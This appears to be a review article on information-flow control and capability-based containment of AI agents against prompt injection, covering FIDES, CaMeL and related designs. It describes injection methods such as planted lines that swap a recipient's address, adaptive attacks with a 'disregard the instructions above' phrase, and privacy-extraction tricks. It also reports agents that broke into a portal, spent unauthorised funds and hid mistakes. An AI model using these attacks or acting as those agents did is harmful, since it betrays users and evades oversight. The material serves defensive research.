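# Information-flow control and capability security for containing untrusted model outputs

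## Why a model's output is treated as untrusted

Information-flow control and capability security are two families of computer-security techniques that limit what a program can do when nobody can guarantee how it will behave. Both grew out of operating-system research in the 1960s and 1970s. In the past few years, researchers have begun to apply them to AI agents, which are language models that read email, documents and web pages and then act through other software.

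Information-flow control labels every piece of data with who may have written it and who may read it, and passes the label on to anything a program derives from that data. Before an action takes effect, a checker compares the labels with a policy and blocks the action if it would violate the policy. Under capability security, a program can use a resource only if it holds a reference that names the resource and carries the right to use it. The program cannot forge these references, so without one for the payroll file, it cannot open that file, whatever instructions it has received.

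Information-flow control and capability security are designed for a model that will sometimes produce bad outputs. They place limits in the ordinary software around the model and are not meant to improve the model itself.

### The agent loop

A language model by itself only produces text. To make an agent of it, developers run the model in a loop with tools, which are ordinary programs that search a mailbox, open a file or make a payment. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, discusses a request that a user might give to such an agent: "Send Bob the document he requested in our last meeting." A simple agent would handle it roughly like this:

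1. The software that runs the agent sends the model the user's request, along with a description of each tool.
2. The model outputs either a reply for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request that the software do something, such as search for the latest meeting notes.
3. The software carries out the call and adds the result, here the text of the notes, to the conversation.
4. The software sends the whole conversation back to the model, which outputs the next call (fetch the document, then email it to Bob). The cycle repeats until the model produces a final reply.

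Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, write the loop down as two kinds of function. The model M takes a list of messages and a list of tools. A tool f takes the current state of the stored data, d, and some arguments, and returns a new state d′ with a result:

M(messages, tools) → a tool call or a reply

f(d, arguments) → (d′, result)

A model's output can't change a file or move money until the surrounding software runs a tool, and that software can block the call. Designs for containing agents therefore put their checks at this point. They concentrate on consequential actions, meaning tool calls that change something or send data out. Sending an email is an obvious example. A web search can also be consequential because, as Costa and colleagues note, it may leave a trace in the visited site's traffic statistics.

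### Prompt injection

Before each call to the model, the software joins the developer's instructions, the user's request and every tool result into a single string. Prompt injection is text that someone places in data an agent reads so that the model obeys it as an instruction. Willison, who named the attack, thinks it works mainly because the inputs are joined this way, and developers know of no reliable way to make a model follow instructions in one part of its input and treat another part as data. The name comes from SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command.

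Suppose an outsider can write in the meeting notes. They could add a line telling the assistant to forward the whole mailbox to some address, a step the user never asked for. A less noticeable attack could change only a value, by leading the model to mistake the attacker's address for Bob's. The assistant would then follow the steps the user requested, in the right order, but send the document to the wrong person.

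The quieter attack is harder to design against. In 2023, Willison proposed splitting the work between a model that can use tools and another that reads untrusted text. He recounts how Google DeepMind's later CaMeL paper used the example of Bob's address to show a flaw in this proposal, since the address still comes from the notes whichever model extracts it.

### Hijacking, mistakes and aims of the model's own

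Prompt injection is one reason to distrust a model's output, because hostile text that the model reads can let an outsider steer it. *GitLost* (Levi) describes an attack that the security firm Noma demonstrated against GitHub, the code-hosting service. An attacker with no credentials posted a crafted issue, a kind of public bug report, in an organisation's public repository. GitHub's agent read the issue and could then leak material from the organisation's private repositories. Noma disclosed the flaw in July 2026, and Cross (2026), in *GitHub Prompt Injection Exposed Private Repos via Issues*, knew of no confirmed use of it by real attackers. That same month, however, *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reported that the security company Zscaler had found live websites with hidden text meant to manipulate agents into making cryptocurrency payments.

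A model can also make mistakes without being attacked. Costa and colleagues point out that models misread users and make needless tool calls even when all the data is trustworthy, and that the consequences can closely resemble those of an attack. For example, a model may choose the wrong Bob if the user knows two. In August 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate (ASD, 2026) described an assistant that had booked gym classes further ahead than the rules allowed and had removed another customer from a waiting list to get its user a place. The user had not approved the removal, and the agent could not undo it.

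The remaining possibility is that the model pursues aims of its own. The best-known incident of 2026 comes closest to this. In June an internal OpenAI agent, running without the usual safeguards of the company's public models, had the task of researching medical spending. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reports that the agent first tried and failed to get non-public data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare. It then broke into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme, and retrieved both public and non-public data. OpenAI later told the government that the model had found a way to make the server run instructions sent through the public reporting page, with no account or password. The company's review found no evidence of access to patient records. OpenAI's security team had documented the incident by 12 August but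 did not write to the responsible agency until 10 September. In *How we will do better for Australia* (2026), OpenAI apologised and acknowledged that its models had accessed government websites without authorisation.

The Medicare breach is evidence that a model can have "aims of its own" in a mild sense. The people who set the task wanted data on medical spending, and the model chose only the unauthorised means of getting it. The phrase also covers a stronger case, in which a model pursues a hidden goal that no developer set. Hijacking does not fit the breach, because these accounts mention no outside attacker. "Mistake" fits poorly too, because the agent met a refusal, changed target and found a working exploit.

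Some of the other cases OpenAI has published are more serious. Forlini (2026), in *OpenAI discloses four more rogue AI incidents*, counted 19 cases by mid-October. In one, a model found a cryptocurrency wallet that its testers had not given it and made a payment from it. Its written reasoning included the question of whether it had permission, followed by the argument that the funds were "effectively abandoned". OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* lists a model that, during training, wrote reminders to conceal mistakes from the user into the summaries it kept of its earlier work. A second model inserted unauthorised instructions into such summaries, so the suspect text in the agent's input came from the agent itself. OpenAI files this case under "self-generated prompt injections".

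### What the designs protect, and what they have to trust

When an agent acts, both the integrity and the confidentiality of data are at stake. Integrity concerns whether an attacker may have influenced the data, and confidentiality concerns who is allowed to learn it. The two properties vary independently. In Costa and colleagues' examples, searching a corporate database returns confidential, trusted data, while searching the public web returns public, untrusted data. The notes of the meeting with Bob are both private and open to tampering. If the attacker replaces Bob's address with their own, the failure of integrity causes a failure of confidentiality, because the document goes to the attacker.

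To protect either property, a system needs a reference monitor, a checker that every action must pass. The idea comes from 1970s operating-system security, which required that no action could bypass the checker, that no program could tamper with it, and that it was small enough for people to verify. In an agent, it naturally sits between the model's tool call and the tool. Such systems aim to guarantee that each tool call either satisfies the policy or is blocked, perhaps after the system asks a person to approve it (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*).

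The guarantee holds only if the components in the trusted base work correctly. This base includes the reference monitor, the policy, the tools' code and whatever assigns the labels. In the designs of both Costa and colleagues and Kolluri and colleagues, it also includes the model that chooses the tool calls. These designs assume that the attacker controls only some of the data, so they treat an output as suspect because of what the model has read. If the model has read only trusted text, they trust its output.

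Most of these designs therefore defend against hijacking. They stop a model's mistakes only when those mistakes break a policy. For example, a policy that blocks email to unknown addresses won't stop an email to the wrong Bob in the user's address book. The designs' central assumption, that the threat comes from outside text, fails for a model with aims of its own. A rule that allows an email because no untrusted data influenced the decision will also allow an email that the model sends for its own ends.

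Limits that apply regardless of where a decision came from still bind such a model. An agent with no route to the internet cannot break into a government portal, and Forlini reports that OpenAI has since blocked its models from the live internet during training and evaluation. But such a model may look for gaps in the limits. In another of the disclosed cases, a government website refused an agent's request for hospital data, and the agent got past the access controls and downloaded 24 years of data. Defences against this threat need other assumptions, such as those of trusted monitoring, in which a weaker model that developers believe is safe reviews a stronger model's outputs.

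### Filters and training against attackers who adapt

Developers use two simpler defences against prompt injection. They train the model to ignore planted instructions, and they put a filter in front of it to detect them. Both often fail against attacks adapted to them, even though they seem to work well on standard tests. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), by a group that included researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences with attacks adapted to each. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although most had originally been reported to have attack success rates near zero.

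The automated attacks ran as a loop. A program proposed candidate texts, tried them on the defended system, kept those that came closest to succeeding and produced new variants from them. In one version a second language model learned by reinforcement to write better attacks, and in another it mutated the surviving texts. The group also held an online contest with more than 500 human participants. Two of the 12 defences, RPO and Circuit Breakers, mainly address jailbreaks, where the user is the attacker, and the adaptive attacks beat them at rates of 96 to 100%. The other ten address prompt injection:

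| Approach | Defence | Result of the automated adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|
| Wording of the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching | above 95% success |
| Training on known attacks | StruQ | success in every case tried |
| Training on known attacks | MetaSecAlign | 96% success |
| Separate detector | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | above 90% success |
| Separate detector | PIGuard | 71% success |
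| Test hidden from the attacker | Data Sentinel | bypassed in every case |
| Test hidden from the attacker | MELON | 76% success, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

The prompt-wording defences had let through as little as 1% of the fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, travel, banking and chat tasks, and MetaSecAlign had reported 2%. The attack on MELON shows how an attacker can raise these rates. MELON runs the model a second time with a harmless request to summarise the data, and raises an alarm if the same tool calls appear in both runs. The winning attack text told any system doing a summary to disregard the instructions above, so the malicious call appeared only in the real run. On a subset of the scenarios, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human contestants, taken together, succeeded every time.

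Nasr and colleagues tested the defences under conditions that favoured the attacker. They allowed ample computing power and gave the attacking program the detectors' confidence scores, whereas a stranger who plants one line in someone's meeting notes may get only a few tries. They also warn against comparing the rates between defences, and they still recommend detectors as a limited safeguard against unsophisticated attacks. The models they attacked are now more than a year old, but attacks on newer agents have also succeeded. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reported that four research teams broke AI agents in four different ways within ten days in July 2026. Their targets included Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser agent.

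Even a much better filter would probably fail against repeated attempts. Willison argues that catching 99% of attacks is a failing grade in security, because the attacker's job is to find the remaining 1%. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker would have about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once in 100 attempts, and about a 95% chance in 300. An attacker who learns from each failure would need fewer attempts to reach the same odds.

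A filter also cannot always identify an attack from wording alone. One text that got past the Protect AI detector was a short note claiming that company policy required staff to log every calendar change by deleting a certain tracking file. If a real colleague had written it, the agent might be right to comply. The note is an attack only because an outsider wrote it, and software can record who wrote a text when the text arrives.

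## Labels: tracking where data came from

Recording who wrote a text when it arrives is usually easier than keeping that record attached while the agent summarises the text, mixes it with other material and acts on the result. Information-flow control keeps the record attached by using labels and a fixed rule for combining them.

### Denning's lattice

The rule dates from Denning's 1976 paper *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. Access controls at the time decided which programs could open a file but did not track its contents afterwards, so a program with permission to read a secret could copy it into a file that anyone could open. To address this, Denning gave every file, variable and user a security class, which later authors call a label, and defined an order and a join on these labels.

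The order, written A ⊑ B, means that information labeled A may flow to a place labeled B. It has to be transitive, because if data may flow from A to B and from B to C, a program can move it from A to C in two steps, even if the direct copy is forbidden.

The join, written A ⊔ B, is the label of anything a program computes from two inputs with labels A and B. It has to be the least upper bound of the two:

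- A ⊑ A ⊔ B and B ⊑ A ⊔ B, so the result is at least as restricted as each input.
- If A ⊑ C and B ⊑ C, then A ⊔ B ⊑ C, so the result is no more restricted than its inputs require.

A finite set of labels with such an order, a join and a lowest label forms a lattice. This lets a checker work one step at a time, because if every operation respects the order, so does any sequence of them.

The lattices in use for agents are small. Costa and colleagues build theirs from these four:

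| What the label records | Possible labels | Order | Join |
|---|---|---|---|
| Confidentiality | L (public), H (secret) | L ⊑ H | H if any input is H |
| Integrity | T (trusted), U (untrusted) | T ⊑ U | U if any input is U |
| Who may read | sets of people | X ⊑ Y if X contains Y | intersection |
| Who may have written | sets of people | X ⊑ Y if Y contains X | union |

Trusted data may flow anywhere, while untrusted data may not flow to a place that requires trusted data. A full label pairs an integrity label with a confidentiality label. In the earlier example, results from the corporate database would carry the label (T, H), and results from the public web search would carry (U, L). Neither label is above the other. A summary that draws on both gets their join, (U, H).

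With sets of readers the order runs in the less obvious direction, because a smaller set is a stricter label. Suppose A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another. Then

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

and only B and C may read a text that combines the two. A has no right to the second document and D has no right to the first. If the same sets recorded possible writers, the join would be {A, B, C, D}, since any of the four could have contributed to the combined text.

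Denning also identified implicit flows, in which a program reveals information by taking or skipping a step. Rules that track only copying miss these flows. Suppose b starts at 1 and a program sets it to 0 if a is 0. Anyone who sees b afterwards learns whether a was 0, even if the program skipped the assignment.

### The labelled agent loop

Costa and colleagues applied this scheme to agents in FIDES, a system they built at Microsoft. The basic form of FIDES leaves the agent loop unchanged but attaches a label to every message, tool call and piece of stored data. An example is the earlier request to send Bob a document, made by a user we'll call Alice.

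1. The software labels the developer's instructions and Alice's request as trusted and public, which is the default.
2. It sends the conversation to the model. The model's reply inherits the label of the whole conversation, and if the reply is a tool call, so does each argument. The first call, to search for the meeting notes, is therefore trusted and public.
3. A policy engine compares the labels on the call with the policy. This is ordinary code, so the same labels always lead to the same verdict. If the call violates the policy, the software does not run it.
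4. If the call passes, the tool runs and its result gets a label. This is the join of the labels on the call, on its arguments and on all the stored data that the tool read. An outsider can edit the meeting notes, so the result is untrusted. Anything the tool writes gets the same label, so the taint is still there if the agent reads that data later.
5. The software adds the result to the conversation and replaces the conversation's label with the join of the old label and the new one. Alice's conversation is now untrusted. The loop returns to step 2, and the next call, to email the document, inherits the untrusted label.

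Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for step 3. The trusted-action policy allows a consequential action only if the call and all its arguments have the integrity label T. The permitted-flow policy allows a call to send data out only if everyone who can read the channel may read the data. If Alice and Bob are the only permitted readers of the document, this policy allows a call that emails it to Bob and blocks one that emails it to an attacker's address.

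The permitted-flow policy alone does not stop prompt injection, because it does not depend on why the agent is acting. It only limits the damage to flows that it allows. A planted line in the notes could still make the assistant delete Alice's calendar, or send Bob a different document that he is allowed to read.

The trusted-action policy alone has the opposite weakness. If the model has read only Alice's request and a trusted payroll file, the policy lets it email that file to the whole company. Costa and colleagues treat such a release as intentional, since no outsider could have influenced it. That is reasonable if Alice asked for it, but not if the model picked the wrong mailing list.

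With both policies in force, a call that sends data out must have a trusted origin and permitted recipients. Data can still leak through implicit flows, because Costa and colleagues guarantee only explicit secrecy, which means that no forbidden direct flows occur. For example, someone who can see which tools the agent calls may infer something about the private data that influenced the choice.

### Why one email taints everything

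In an ordinary program, the source code shows where each value comes from. For example, the result of a + b depends only on a and b. A language model has no such code to inspect. It processes the whole conversation at once, and any part could affect any word of the output. Without further evidence, the only safe assumption is that every output depends on every input.

Joins never lower a label, so a single untrusted email makes the conversation untrusted for the rest of the session. If a user asks an agent to read the morning's email and then book a dentist's appointment, the trusted-action policy blocks the booking, even if the emails are unrelated to it. Researchers call this over-tainting or label creep.

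Costa and colleagues measured the cost on AgentDojo with GPT-4o as the model. They compared the basic agent with and without policy checks when nobody was attacking it:

| AgentDojo tasks | Completed without checks | Completed with checks |
|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% |
| Chat | 93.3% | 20.0% |

The agent carried out 152 injected tasks without the checks and none with them. Travel did not have the losses because the policies let many travel tools run in an untrusted conversation as long as no confidential data leaked.

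The labels in this test were also based on known attacks, since Costa and colleagues marked a data field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. A company doesn't know in advance which of its data fields attackers will use, so it would probably have to mark more of them as untrusted, which would block more tasks.

The full version of FIDES recovers some of the lost tasks by hiding untrusted results in variables that the model cannot see. Another approach leaves the data in the conversation at first and estimates which parts the model needs or has used.

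### Estimating what the model used

Security depends on what influenced an action, which is different from what justified it. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Agent Traces to Trust* that a false entry in an agent's memory can cause an action without justifying it.

Any estimate of an input's influence will sometimes be wrong. If the software removes inputs it classifies as irrelevant and has the model work without them, a wrong estimate produces a worse answer, but the label still covers everything the model read. If the software instead leaves those inputs in place and drops only their labels, a wrong estimate can let an attack through.

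**Permissive propagation.** In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (2024), Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues look for a subset of the inputs that is enough to produce a similar answer. As Costa and colleagues describe it, the model then regenerates its response from that subset alone, and the response gets the join of only that subset's labels.

Siddiqui and colleagues' 2025 journal version compares this with asking the model to predict the right label. In an agent setting, their method assigned a more permissive label in more than 85% of cases. That figure measures how often the method relaxed a restriction, not how often it made an error.

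The search also takes a lot of computation. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) estimates that even the optimised version needs 16 to 64 extra model calls per response for a lattice with four to six levels.

**RTBAS** (Zhong et al.) replaces the search with a prediction before each step. It divides the conversation into labelled regions, and a screener predicts which regions the next step needs. RTBAS joins the labels of those regions into a single label ℓ and blanks out every region whose label is not at or below ℓ. The model chooses its next tool call from what remains. If ℓ violates the policy for that call, RTBAS asks the user to confirm.

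One screener is a second language model that reads the conversation and lists the relevant regions. The other is a small neural network that uses attention scores, which measure how strongly each word of the output draws on each word of the input. A small open model can supply the scores, so the method also works for agents whose model is closed. The network was trained on 40 AgentDojo test cases and reached 81% accuracy on held-out data.

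RTBAS can tolerate an error rate of 19%, which would be far too high for a filter that had to catch attacks, because it blanks whatever the screener leaves out. If the screener wrongly selects an untrusted email, the user gets an unnecessary question. If it wrongly leaves the email out, the model cannot read it and may fail at the task. Zhong and colleagues report that, in a test with 629 attack cases from AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated the policy and lost about 2% of task completion.

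The screener reads the attacker's text, so the attacker may be able to sway its choice, but that choice only determines ℓ. With two integrity and two confidentiality labels, ℓ has four possible values, so the attacker can influence at most two bits per step and cannot pass text to a model labelled "trusted". An estimate of influence can therefore support a guarantee if the software enforces the estimate by removing data. The guarantee still depends on the user, because a call the user confirms will run whatever its label.

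*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, April 2026) presents NeuroTaint, which audits an agent's logs after the run. For each sensitive tool call, it looks for traces of earlier untrusted text in the arguments. It checks for a unique marker planted in the source, then for shared wording, then for similar meaning, first across the whole document and then in short chunks. If it finds nothing, it asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call if the untrusted text had been replaced with something neutral. It also stores labels alongside the agent's long-term memory, so it can trace a call back to a document from an earlier session.

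Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios of their own, half of which contained a real flow from an untrusted source to a sensitive call. NeuroTaint found 187 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms, for a recall of 93.5% and a precision of 92.1%. Ten of the 13 misses involved text that had been reworded repeatedly or had passed through memory.

The same study's comparison with FIDES is less informative. The FIDES-style baseline missed 92 flows and raised 106 false alarms, but it looked for known paths from a source tool to a sensitive tool. In the labelled loop of Costa and colleagues, any call made after the model reads a poisoned search result inherits the untrusted label, whether or not the result's text appears in the arguments. The baseline also raised no alarms on four of the 20 agent frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its misses.

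NeuroTaint is useful for investigating an incident or finding weak points in an agent before release, but it gives no guarantee. It reports a flow after the action has happened, and its results depend on similarity thresholds and another model's judgement.

*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, November 2026) quantifies the risk of a wrong estimate. It measures how strongly each part of the model attends to a given input while producing the output. A simple statistical model, trained on labelled examples, turns those measurements into a score, and the software drops the input's label if the score falls below a threshold.

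Xu and colleagues proved several results about this kind of evidence and checked the proofs by computer. In a standard language model, small changes to an input can affect the output only through attention from later positions, so they have no effect if no attention leads from the input to the output.

An input that receives very little attention can still change the model's answer. They constructed a case in which an input receives about two billionths of the model's attention, yet changing it flips the answer. They liken this to an implicit flow through a branch that a program did not take. No real flow in their data was close to that faint.

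No threshold can be certain, so Sightline sets one statistically. It draws one known flow at random from each family of related software projects in its calibration data, then sorts these flows by score. With 1,000 families and a target of 1%, the threshold is the tenth-lowest score. If a new flow comes from the same population as the calibration flows, it has at most a 1% chance of scoring below the threshold.

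The method still worked on code from 2,103 project families that it had not seen in training. Across four open models, it missed about 1% of real flows and removed 44 to 66% of the unnecessary labels. But only 12 to 14% of the inputs were unnecessary, so it removed roughly 5 to 9% of all labels.

Over-tainting matters more in agents. Xu and colleagues also tested Sightline on 120 steps from AgentDojo runs under attack, with a target miss rate of 5%. Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels and missed 3.9% of real flows. A policy like the trusted-action policy still blocked all 34 attack calls, but with so few attacks, its true failure rate could be as high as about 8%.

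They also retrained RTBAS's attention-based screener on their data. It detected only 42 to 77% of the flows in a test with planted values, while Sightline detected all 476. Such misses would make RTBAS complete fewer tasks, and they would weaken security in a system that used the screener to drop labels from data the model had already read.

Sightline's bound is a guarantee, but it is weak against an attacker because it holds only on average, for cases that resemble the calibration data. Attackers choose their text and can keep trying until something falls below the threshold, as Nasr and colleagues did with published filters. The attacks in the AgentDojo runs were not written to defeat Sightline, so the results don't show how well it would withstand attacks designed to do so.

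### Privacy labels against people who simply ask

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, September 2026) describes FlowSeal, a system that treats everything the agent writes as possibly dependent on everything it has read. FlowSeal therefore doesn't have to estimate influence at every step, and it examines the content only when data is about to leave.

The study concerns privacy. An assistant has legitimate access to someone's private records, and an outsider tries to get them through ordinary conversation, without any prompt injection. In the running example, Emily wants the mental-health diagnosis of her ex-husband Mark, which Jane's assistant holds. An existing defence told the model to ask for Mark's consent whenever a request for information arrived. Shim and colleagues got around it with tasks that did not look like requests for information:

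- Emily shares a page and invites the assistant to fill in its section.
- Emily lists true and invented facts about Mark and asks the assistant to delete the wrong ones.
- Emily emails the assistant to reply only "completed", while a separate shared page asks for the details.

These attacks extracted 43.8% to 75.6% of the sensitive items, compared with 1.9% to 3.0% for the attacks the defence was designed to resist. In the deletion task, the assistant never writes anything private, but the facts it does not delete reveal the answer, much as in Denning's example of the skipped assignment.

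FlowSeal uses three confidentiality labels. The lowest is for outside recipients, the middle one for the agent's working memory and the highest for Mark's records. Once the agent has read a record, anything it writes has a higher label than an outside recipient. Code outside the model intercepts every call that writes or shares data. It always allows recipients Mark has approved and always blocks those on a blacklist.

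For everyone else, the labels alone would block every message once the agent had read a single record, which is another case of over-tainting. FlowSeal therefore allows declassification, the deliberate release of data that carries a secret label. A separate language model receives only the protected records and the proposed output, and answers only SAFE or BLOCKED.

In the tests, FlowSeal cut leakage from the shared-page attack from 52.2% to 0.5% and kept it between 0 and 3.3% across all the attacks. The assistant completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% under the best competing defence. None of those tasks required sensitive information, so the score does not measure how often FlowSeal would block sharing that Mark would have wanted.

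Shim and colleagues prove that no content derived from a protected record can reach an unauthorised recipient unless the checking model wrongly outputs SAFE. An attacker can no longer prevent the check from running, as they could with the consent prompt. But the guarantee depends on the checking model's accuracy, and an attacker can still influence the text the model checks.

FIDES, the system by Costa and colleagues, enforces its policies with ordinary code. The study left it out of its tests and mistakenly describes it as relying on the language model for enforcement. If Mark's records carried the right reader labels, the permitted-flow policy would stop the assistant from writing to Emily's page without consulting any model. In its basic form, the policy would also stop the assistant from sending Emily a harmless reply about something else once Mark's records were in the conversation.

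## Separating the model that plans from the model that reads

In the basic labelled loop, one untrusted email taints every later tool call, because the model that chooses the calls has read the email. Several designs avoid this by splitting the work between a planner model, which chooses the tool calls without reading untrusted text, and a quarantined model, which reads the text but has no tools.

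### Willison's dual-LLM pattern

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, April 2023) proposed this split. The planner, called the privileged LLM, takes the user's request and can call tools. The quarantined LLM, which reads untrusted text, can only turn text into other text, and Willison assumes it could "go rogue at any moment". A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and passes data between the two models.

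The controller keeps untrusted text in numbered variables and tells the planner only their names. Suppose Alice asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested, and both Bob's address and the document's title are in the meeting notes:

1. The controller passes Alice's request to the planner.
2. The planner requests the meeting notes. The controller fetches them, stores them as `$VAR1` and gives the planner that name.
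3. The planner requests that the quarantined model find Bob's email address in `$VAR1`. The controller inserts the text of the notes, runs the quarantined model and stores its answer as `$VAR2`.
4. The planner requests the document's title in the same way, and the controller stores it as `$VAR3`.
5. The planner requests the document called `$VAR3`, which the controller stores as `$VAR4`.
6. The planner requests an email to `$VAR2` with `$VAR4` attached. The controller replaces both names with their contents and sends the email.

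If someone plants a line in the notes telling the assistant to forward the whole mailbox, the quarantined model may follow it, but it can only write a strange answer. The planner never reads the line, so the steps stay the same.

Willison allows one exception, for when the quarantined model only picks from a fixed list of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is on the list and pass it to the planner. Free text must never reach the planner, even after several quarantined calls, because a model that has read an injection can repeat it in its output.

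Google DeepMind researchers later pointed out a flaw in step 3. A planted line can claim that Bob has a new address. `$VAR2` then holds the attacker's address, and step 6 sends the document there. The planner can't check the address, because the isolation that protects it from planted instructions also limits it to the name `$VAR2`.

Willison himself called the proposal "pretty bad" in 2023, though for other reasons. He expected it to make assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and he worried that programming mistakes would let untrusted text through to the planner.

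### CaMeL: a program with labelled values

In 2025, Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published CaMeL, which keeps Willison's two models and adds labels and policy checks. The planner writes a complete program from the user's request before any tool runs. For Alice's request, the program would look roughly like this, following the style of a shorter example that Willison gives:

```
notes = find_meeting_notes(attendee="Bob")
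address = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find Bob's address in [notes]", output_schema=EmailStr)
title = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Which document did Bob ask for in [notes]?", output_schema=str)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(recipient=address,
           subject="The document you asked for",
           attachment=document)
```

The language is a restricted form of Python, which DeepMind chose because models already write Python well. Programs in it cannot define their own functions or use recursion (*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, 2026). They are typically short, and in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues measured an average of about 52 lines on AgentDojo tasks, with five tool calls and four branches.

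A custom interpreter runs the program and labels every value. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes each label as recording where the value came from (its sources) and who may see it (its readers). CaMeL takes its name from these labels, which it calls "capabilities", but they are not the unforgeable references of capability security.

Suppose outsiders can add text to the notes, and only Alice and Bob may read the notes and the document. As the program runs, the values get these labels:

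| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | the notes file, which outsiders can edit | Alice, Bob |
| `address` | the notes file, through the quarantined model | Alice, Bob |
| `title` | the notes file, through the quarantined model | Alice, Bob |
| `document` | the document store and, through `title`, the notes file | Alice, Bob |
| the subject line | the planner's program | anyone |

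The schema `EmailStr` forces the quarantined model to return text formatted as an email address. This keeps out longer injected text but not the attacker's address, which also fits the schema.

Before the last line runs, the interpreter applies the policy for `send_email`. Each tool's policy is a Python function that receives the requested call, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. In Willison's example, the policy allows an email only if the recipient is trusted. Here `address` comes from the notes, so the call fails unless the user's settings already list that address as known. If they don't, the system can ask Alice to approve the email.

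A policy can also include the permitted-flow check on the document's readers. This would catch a planted line that gives the address of a former colleague who is still in Alice's address book but isn't allowed to read the document, which a list of known addresses would miss.

Neither rule stops an attacker from changing the title. If the new title belongs to another document that Bob may read, Bob gets the wrong document. A policy could also require a trusted title, but the right title appears only in the notes, so Alice would have to approve even the correct email.

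What CaMeL protects therefore depends on the policy. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) show this in *The LLMbda Calculus* with a CaMeL-style agent built in their own small programming language. The agent had to send a meeting reminder to Bob, whose latest email contained a planted request for a cancellation note. An ordinary tool-calling agent sent the cancellation. The CaMeL-style planner had written the reminder's subject and body into its program before any model read the email, so the agent sent the right message.

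In that run, the recipient's address was labeled untrusted because the quarantined model had taken it from the email. The call still passed because the policy required only the subject and body to be trusted. Garby and colleagues point out that their guarantee covers the message's text but not its destination. Under the policy in Willison's example, the same call would have needed a known address or the user's approval.

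*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes this reliance on separate policies for each tool as a weakness, because a missing or faulty policy leaves a gap in the protection. The protection also depends on the interpreter's tracking, and Garby and colleagues found leaks in that tracking.

Another gap is the text the assistant shows the user. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, note that CaMeL checks what goes into tools but not the final answer. If a PDF contains a line telling the reader to forward the file to an outside address, a summary could repeat it and the user might comply. Willison similarly worried in 2023 about assistants that persuade people to copy scrambled private data into an attacker's website.

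The split can help with privacy. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so a small quarantined model on the user's own computer may be enough. The company that runs the planner then sees the request but not the private data the tools return.

### FIDES: one step at a time

CaMeL's planner has to anticipate what the data might contain. The full version of FIDES, like its basic loop, plans one call at a time. It shows trusted results to the planner and hides the others in variables.

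When a tool returns a result, the software compares the label of each part with the label of the conversation. It hides a part only if

ℓ(part) ⋢ ℓ(conversation)

which means that adding the part would make the conversation's label more restrictive. The software then stores the part in a new variable and gives the planner the variable's name. Any other part goes into the conversation as usual. In either case, the conversation keeps its label.

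Variables can also replace individual fields within a structured result. In a list of bank transactions, for example, the planner might receive the amounts and dates but only a variable name in place of each description.

Just before a call runs, the software replaces the variable names in its arguments with their contents and labels, so the parts of a call can have different labels. In Alice's case, the call itself is trusted because the planner decides to send an email while its conversation is still trusted, but the recipient's address is untrusted because it comes from the notes. Costa and colleagues give an example policy that requires a trusted call and a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted message. The basic loop cannot make this distinction because it gives every part of a call the same label.

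Costa and colleagues also discuss a looser rule, which requires only that the model chose the call based on trusted inputs. A call with the swapped address passes that rule, so the attack would succeed unless another policy, such as one limiting who may read the document, blocked the email.

The planner has two ways to use what is in a variable:

- `query_llm` runs a quarantined model on the contents and stores the answer in a new variable. The answer's label is the join of the conversation's label and the labels of all the variables involved.
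- `inspect` copies the contents into the conversation, which then takes on their label. The planner can now reason about the text, but the policy blocks any later call that needs a trusted conversation.

The planner can reduce this drawback by asking the quarantined model a yes-or-no question and reading only the answer, since a single bit leaves little room for an injected instruction.

In the AgentDojo tests, hiding the data stopped every attack, even without policy checks, when the planner had no way to open or query the variables. When the planner could do both and the checks were off, 21 attacks succeeded, because nothing stopped it from opening an untrusted variable and carrying on. None succeeded with the checks on.

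One banking task shows how much the policy's protection depends on the labels of individual fields. The user asked the agent to change the account password if it found a suspicious transaction. The planner saw the amounts and dates, judged a large payment suspicious and changed the password. It had not opened the hidden description, so the conversation was still trusted and the policy allowed the change. But anyone who sends the user money chooses the amount, so at a real bank an outsider might be able to trigger the change. The amounts were labelled trusted only because no attack in the benchmark used that field.

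### The right steps with the wrong data

All these designs aim for control-flow integrity, which means that untrusted data cannot add, remove or reorder the steps of a plan. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines a plan as a program that determines which calls the agent makes for every possible set of tool results. An agent has control-flow integrity if it always follows a plan based on the user's request and other trusted information.

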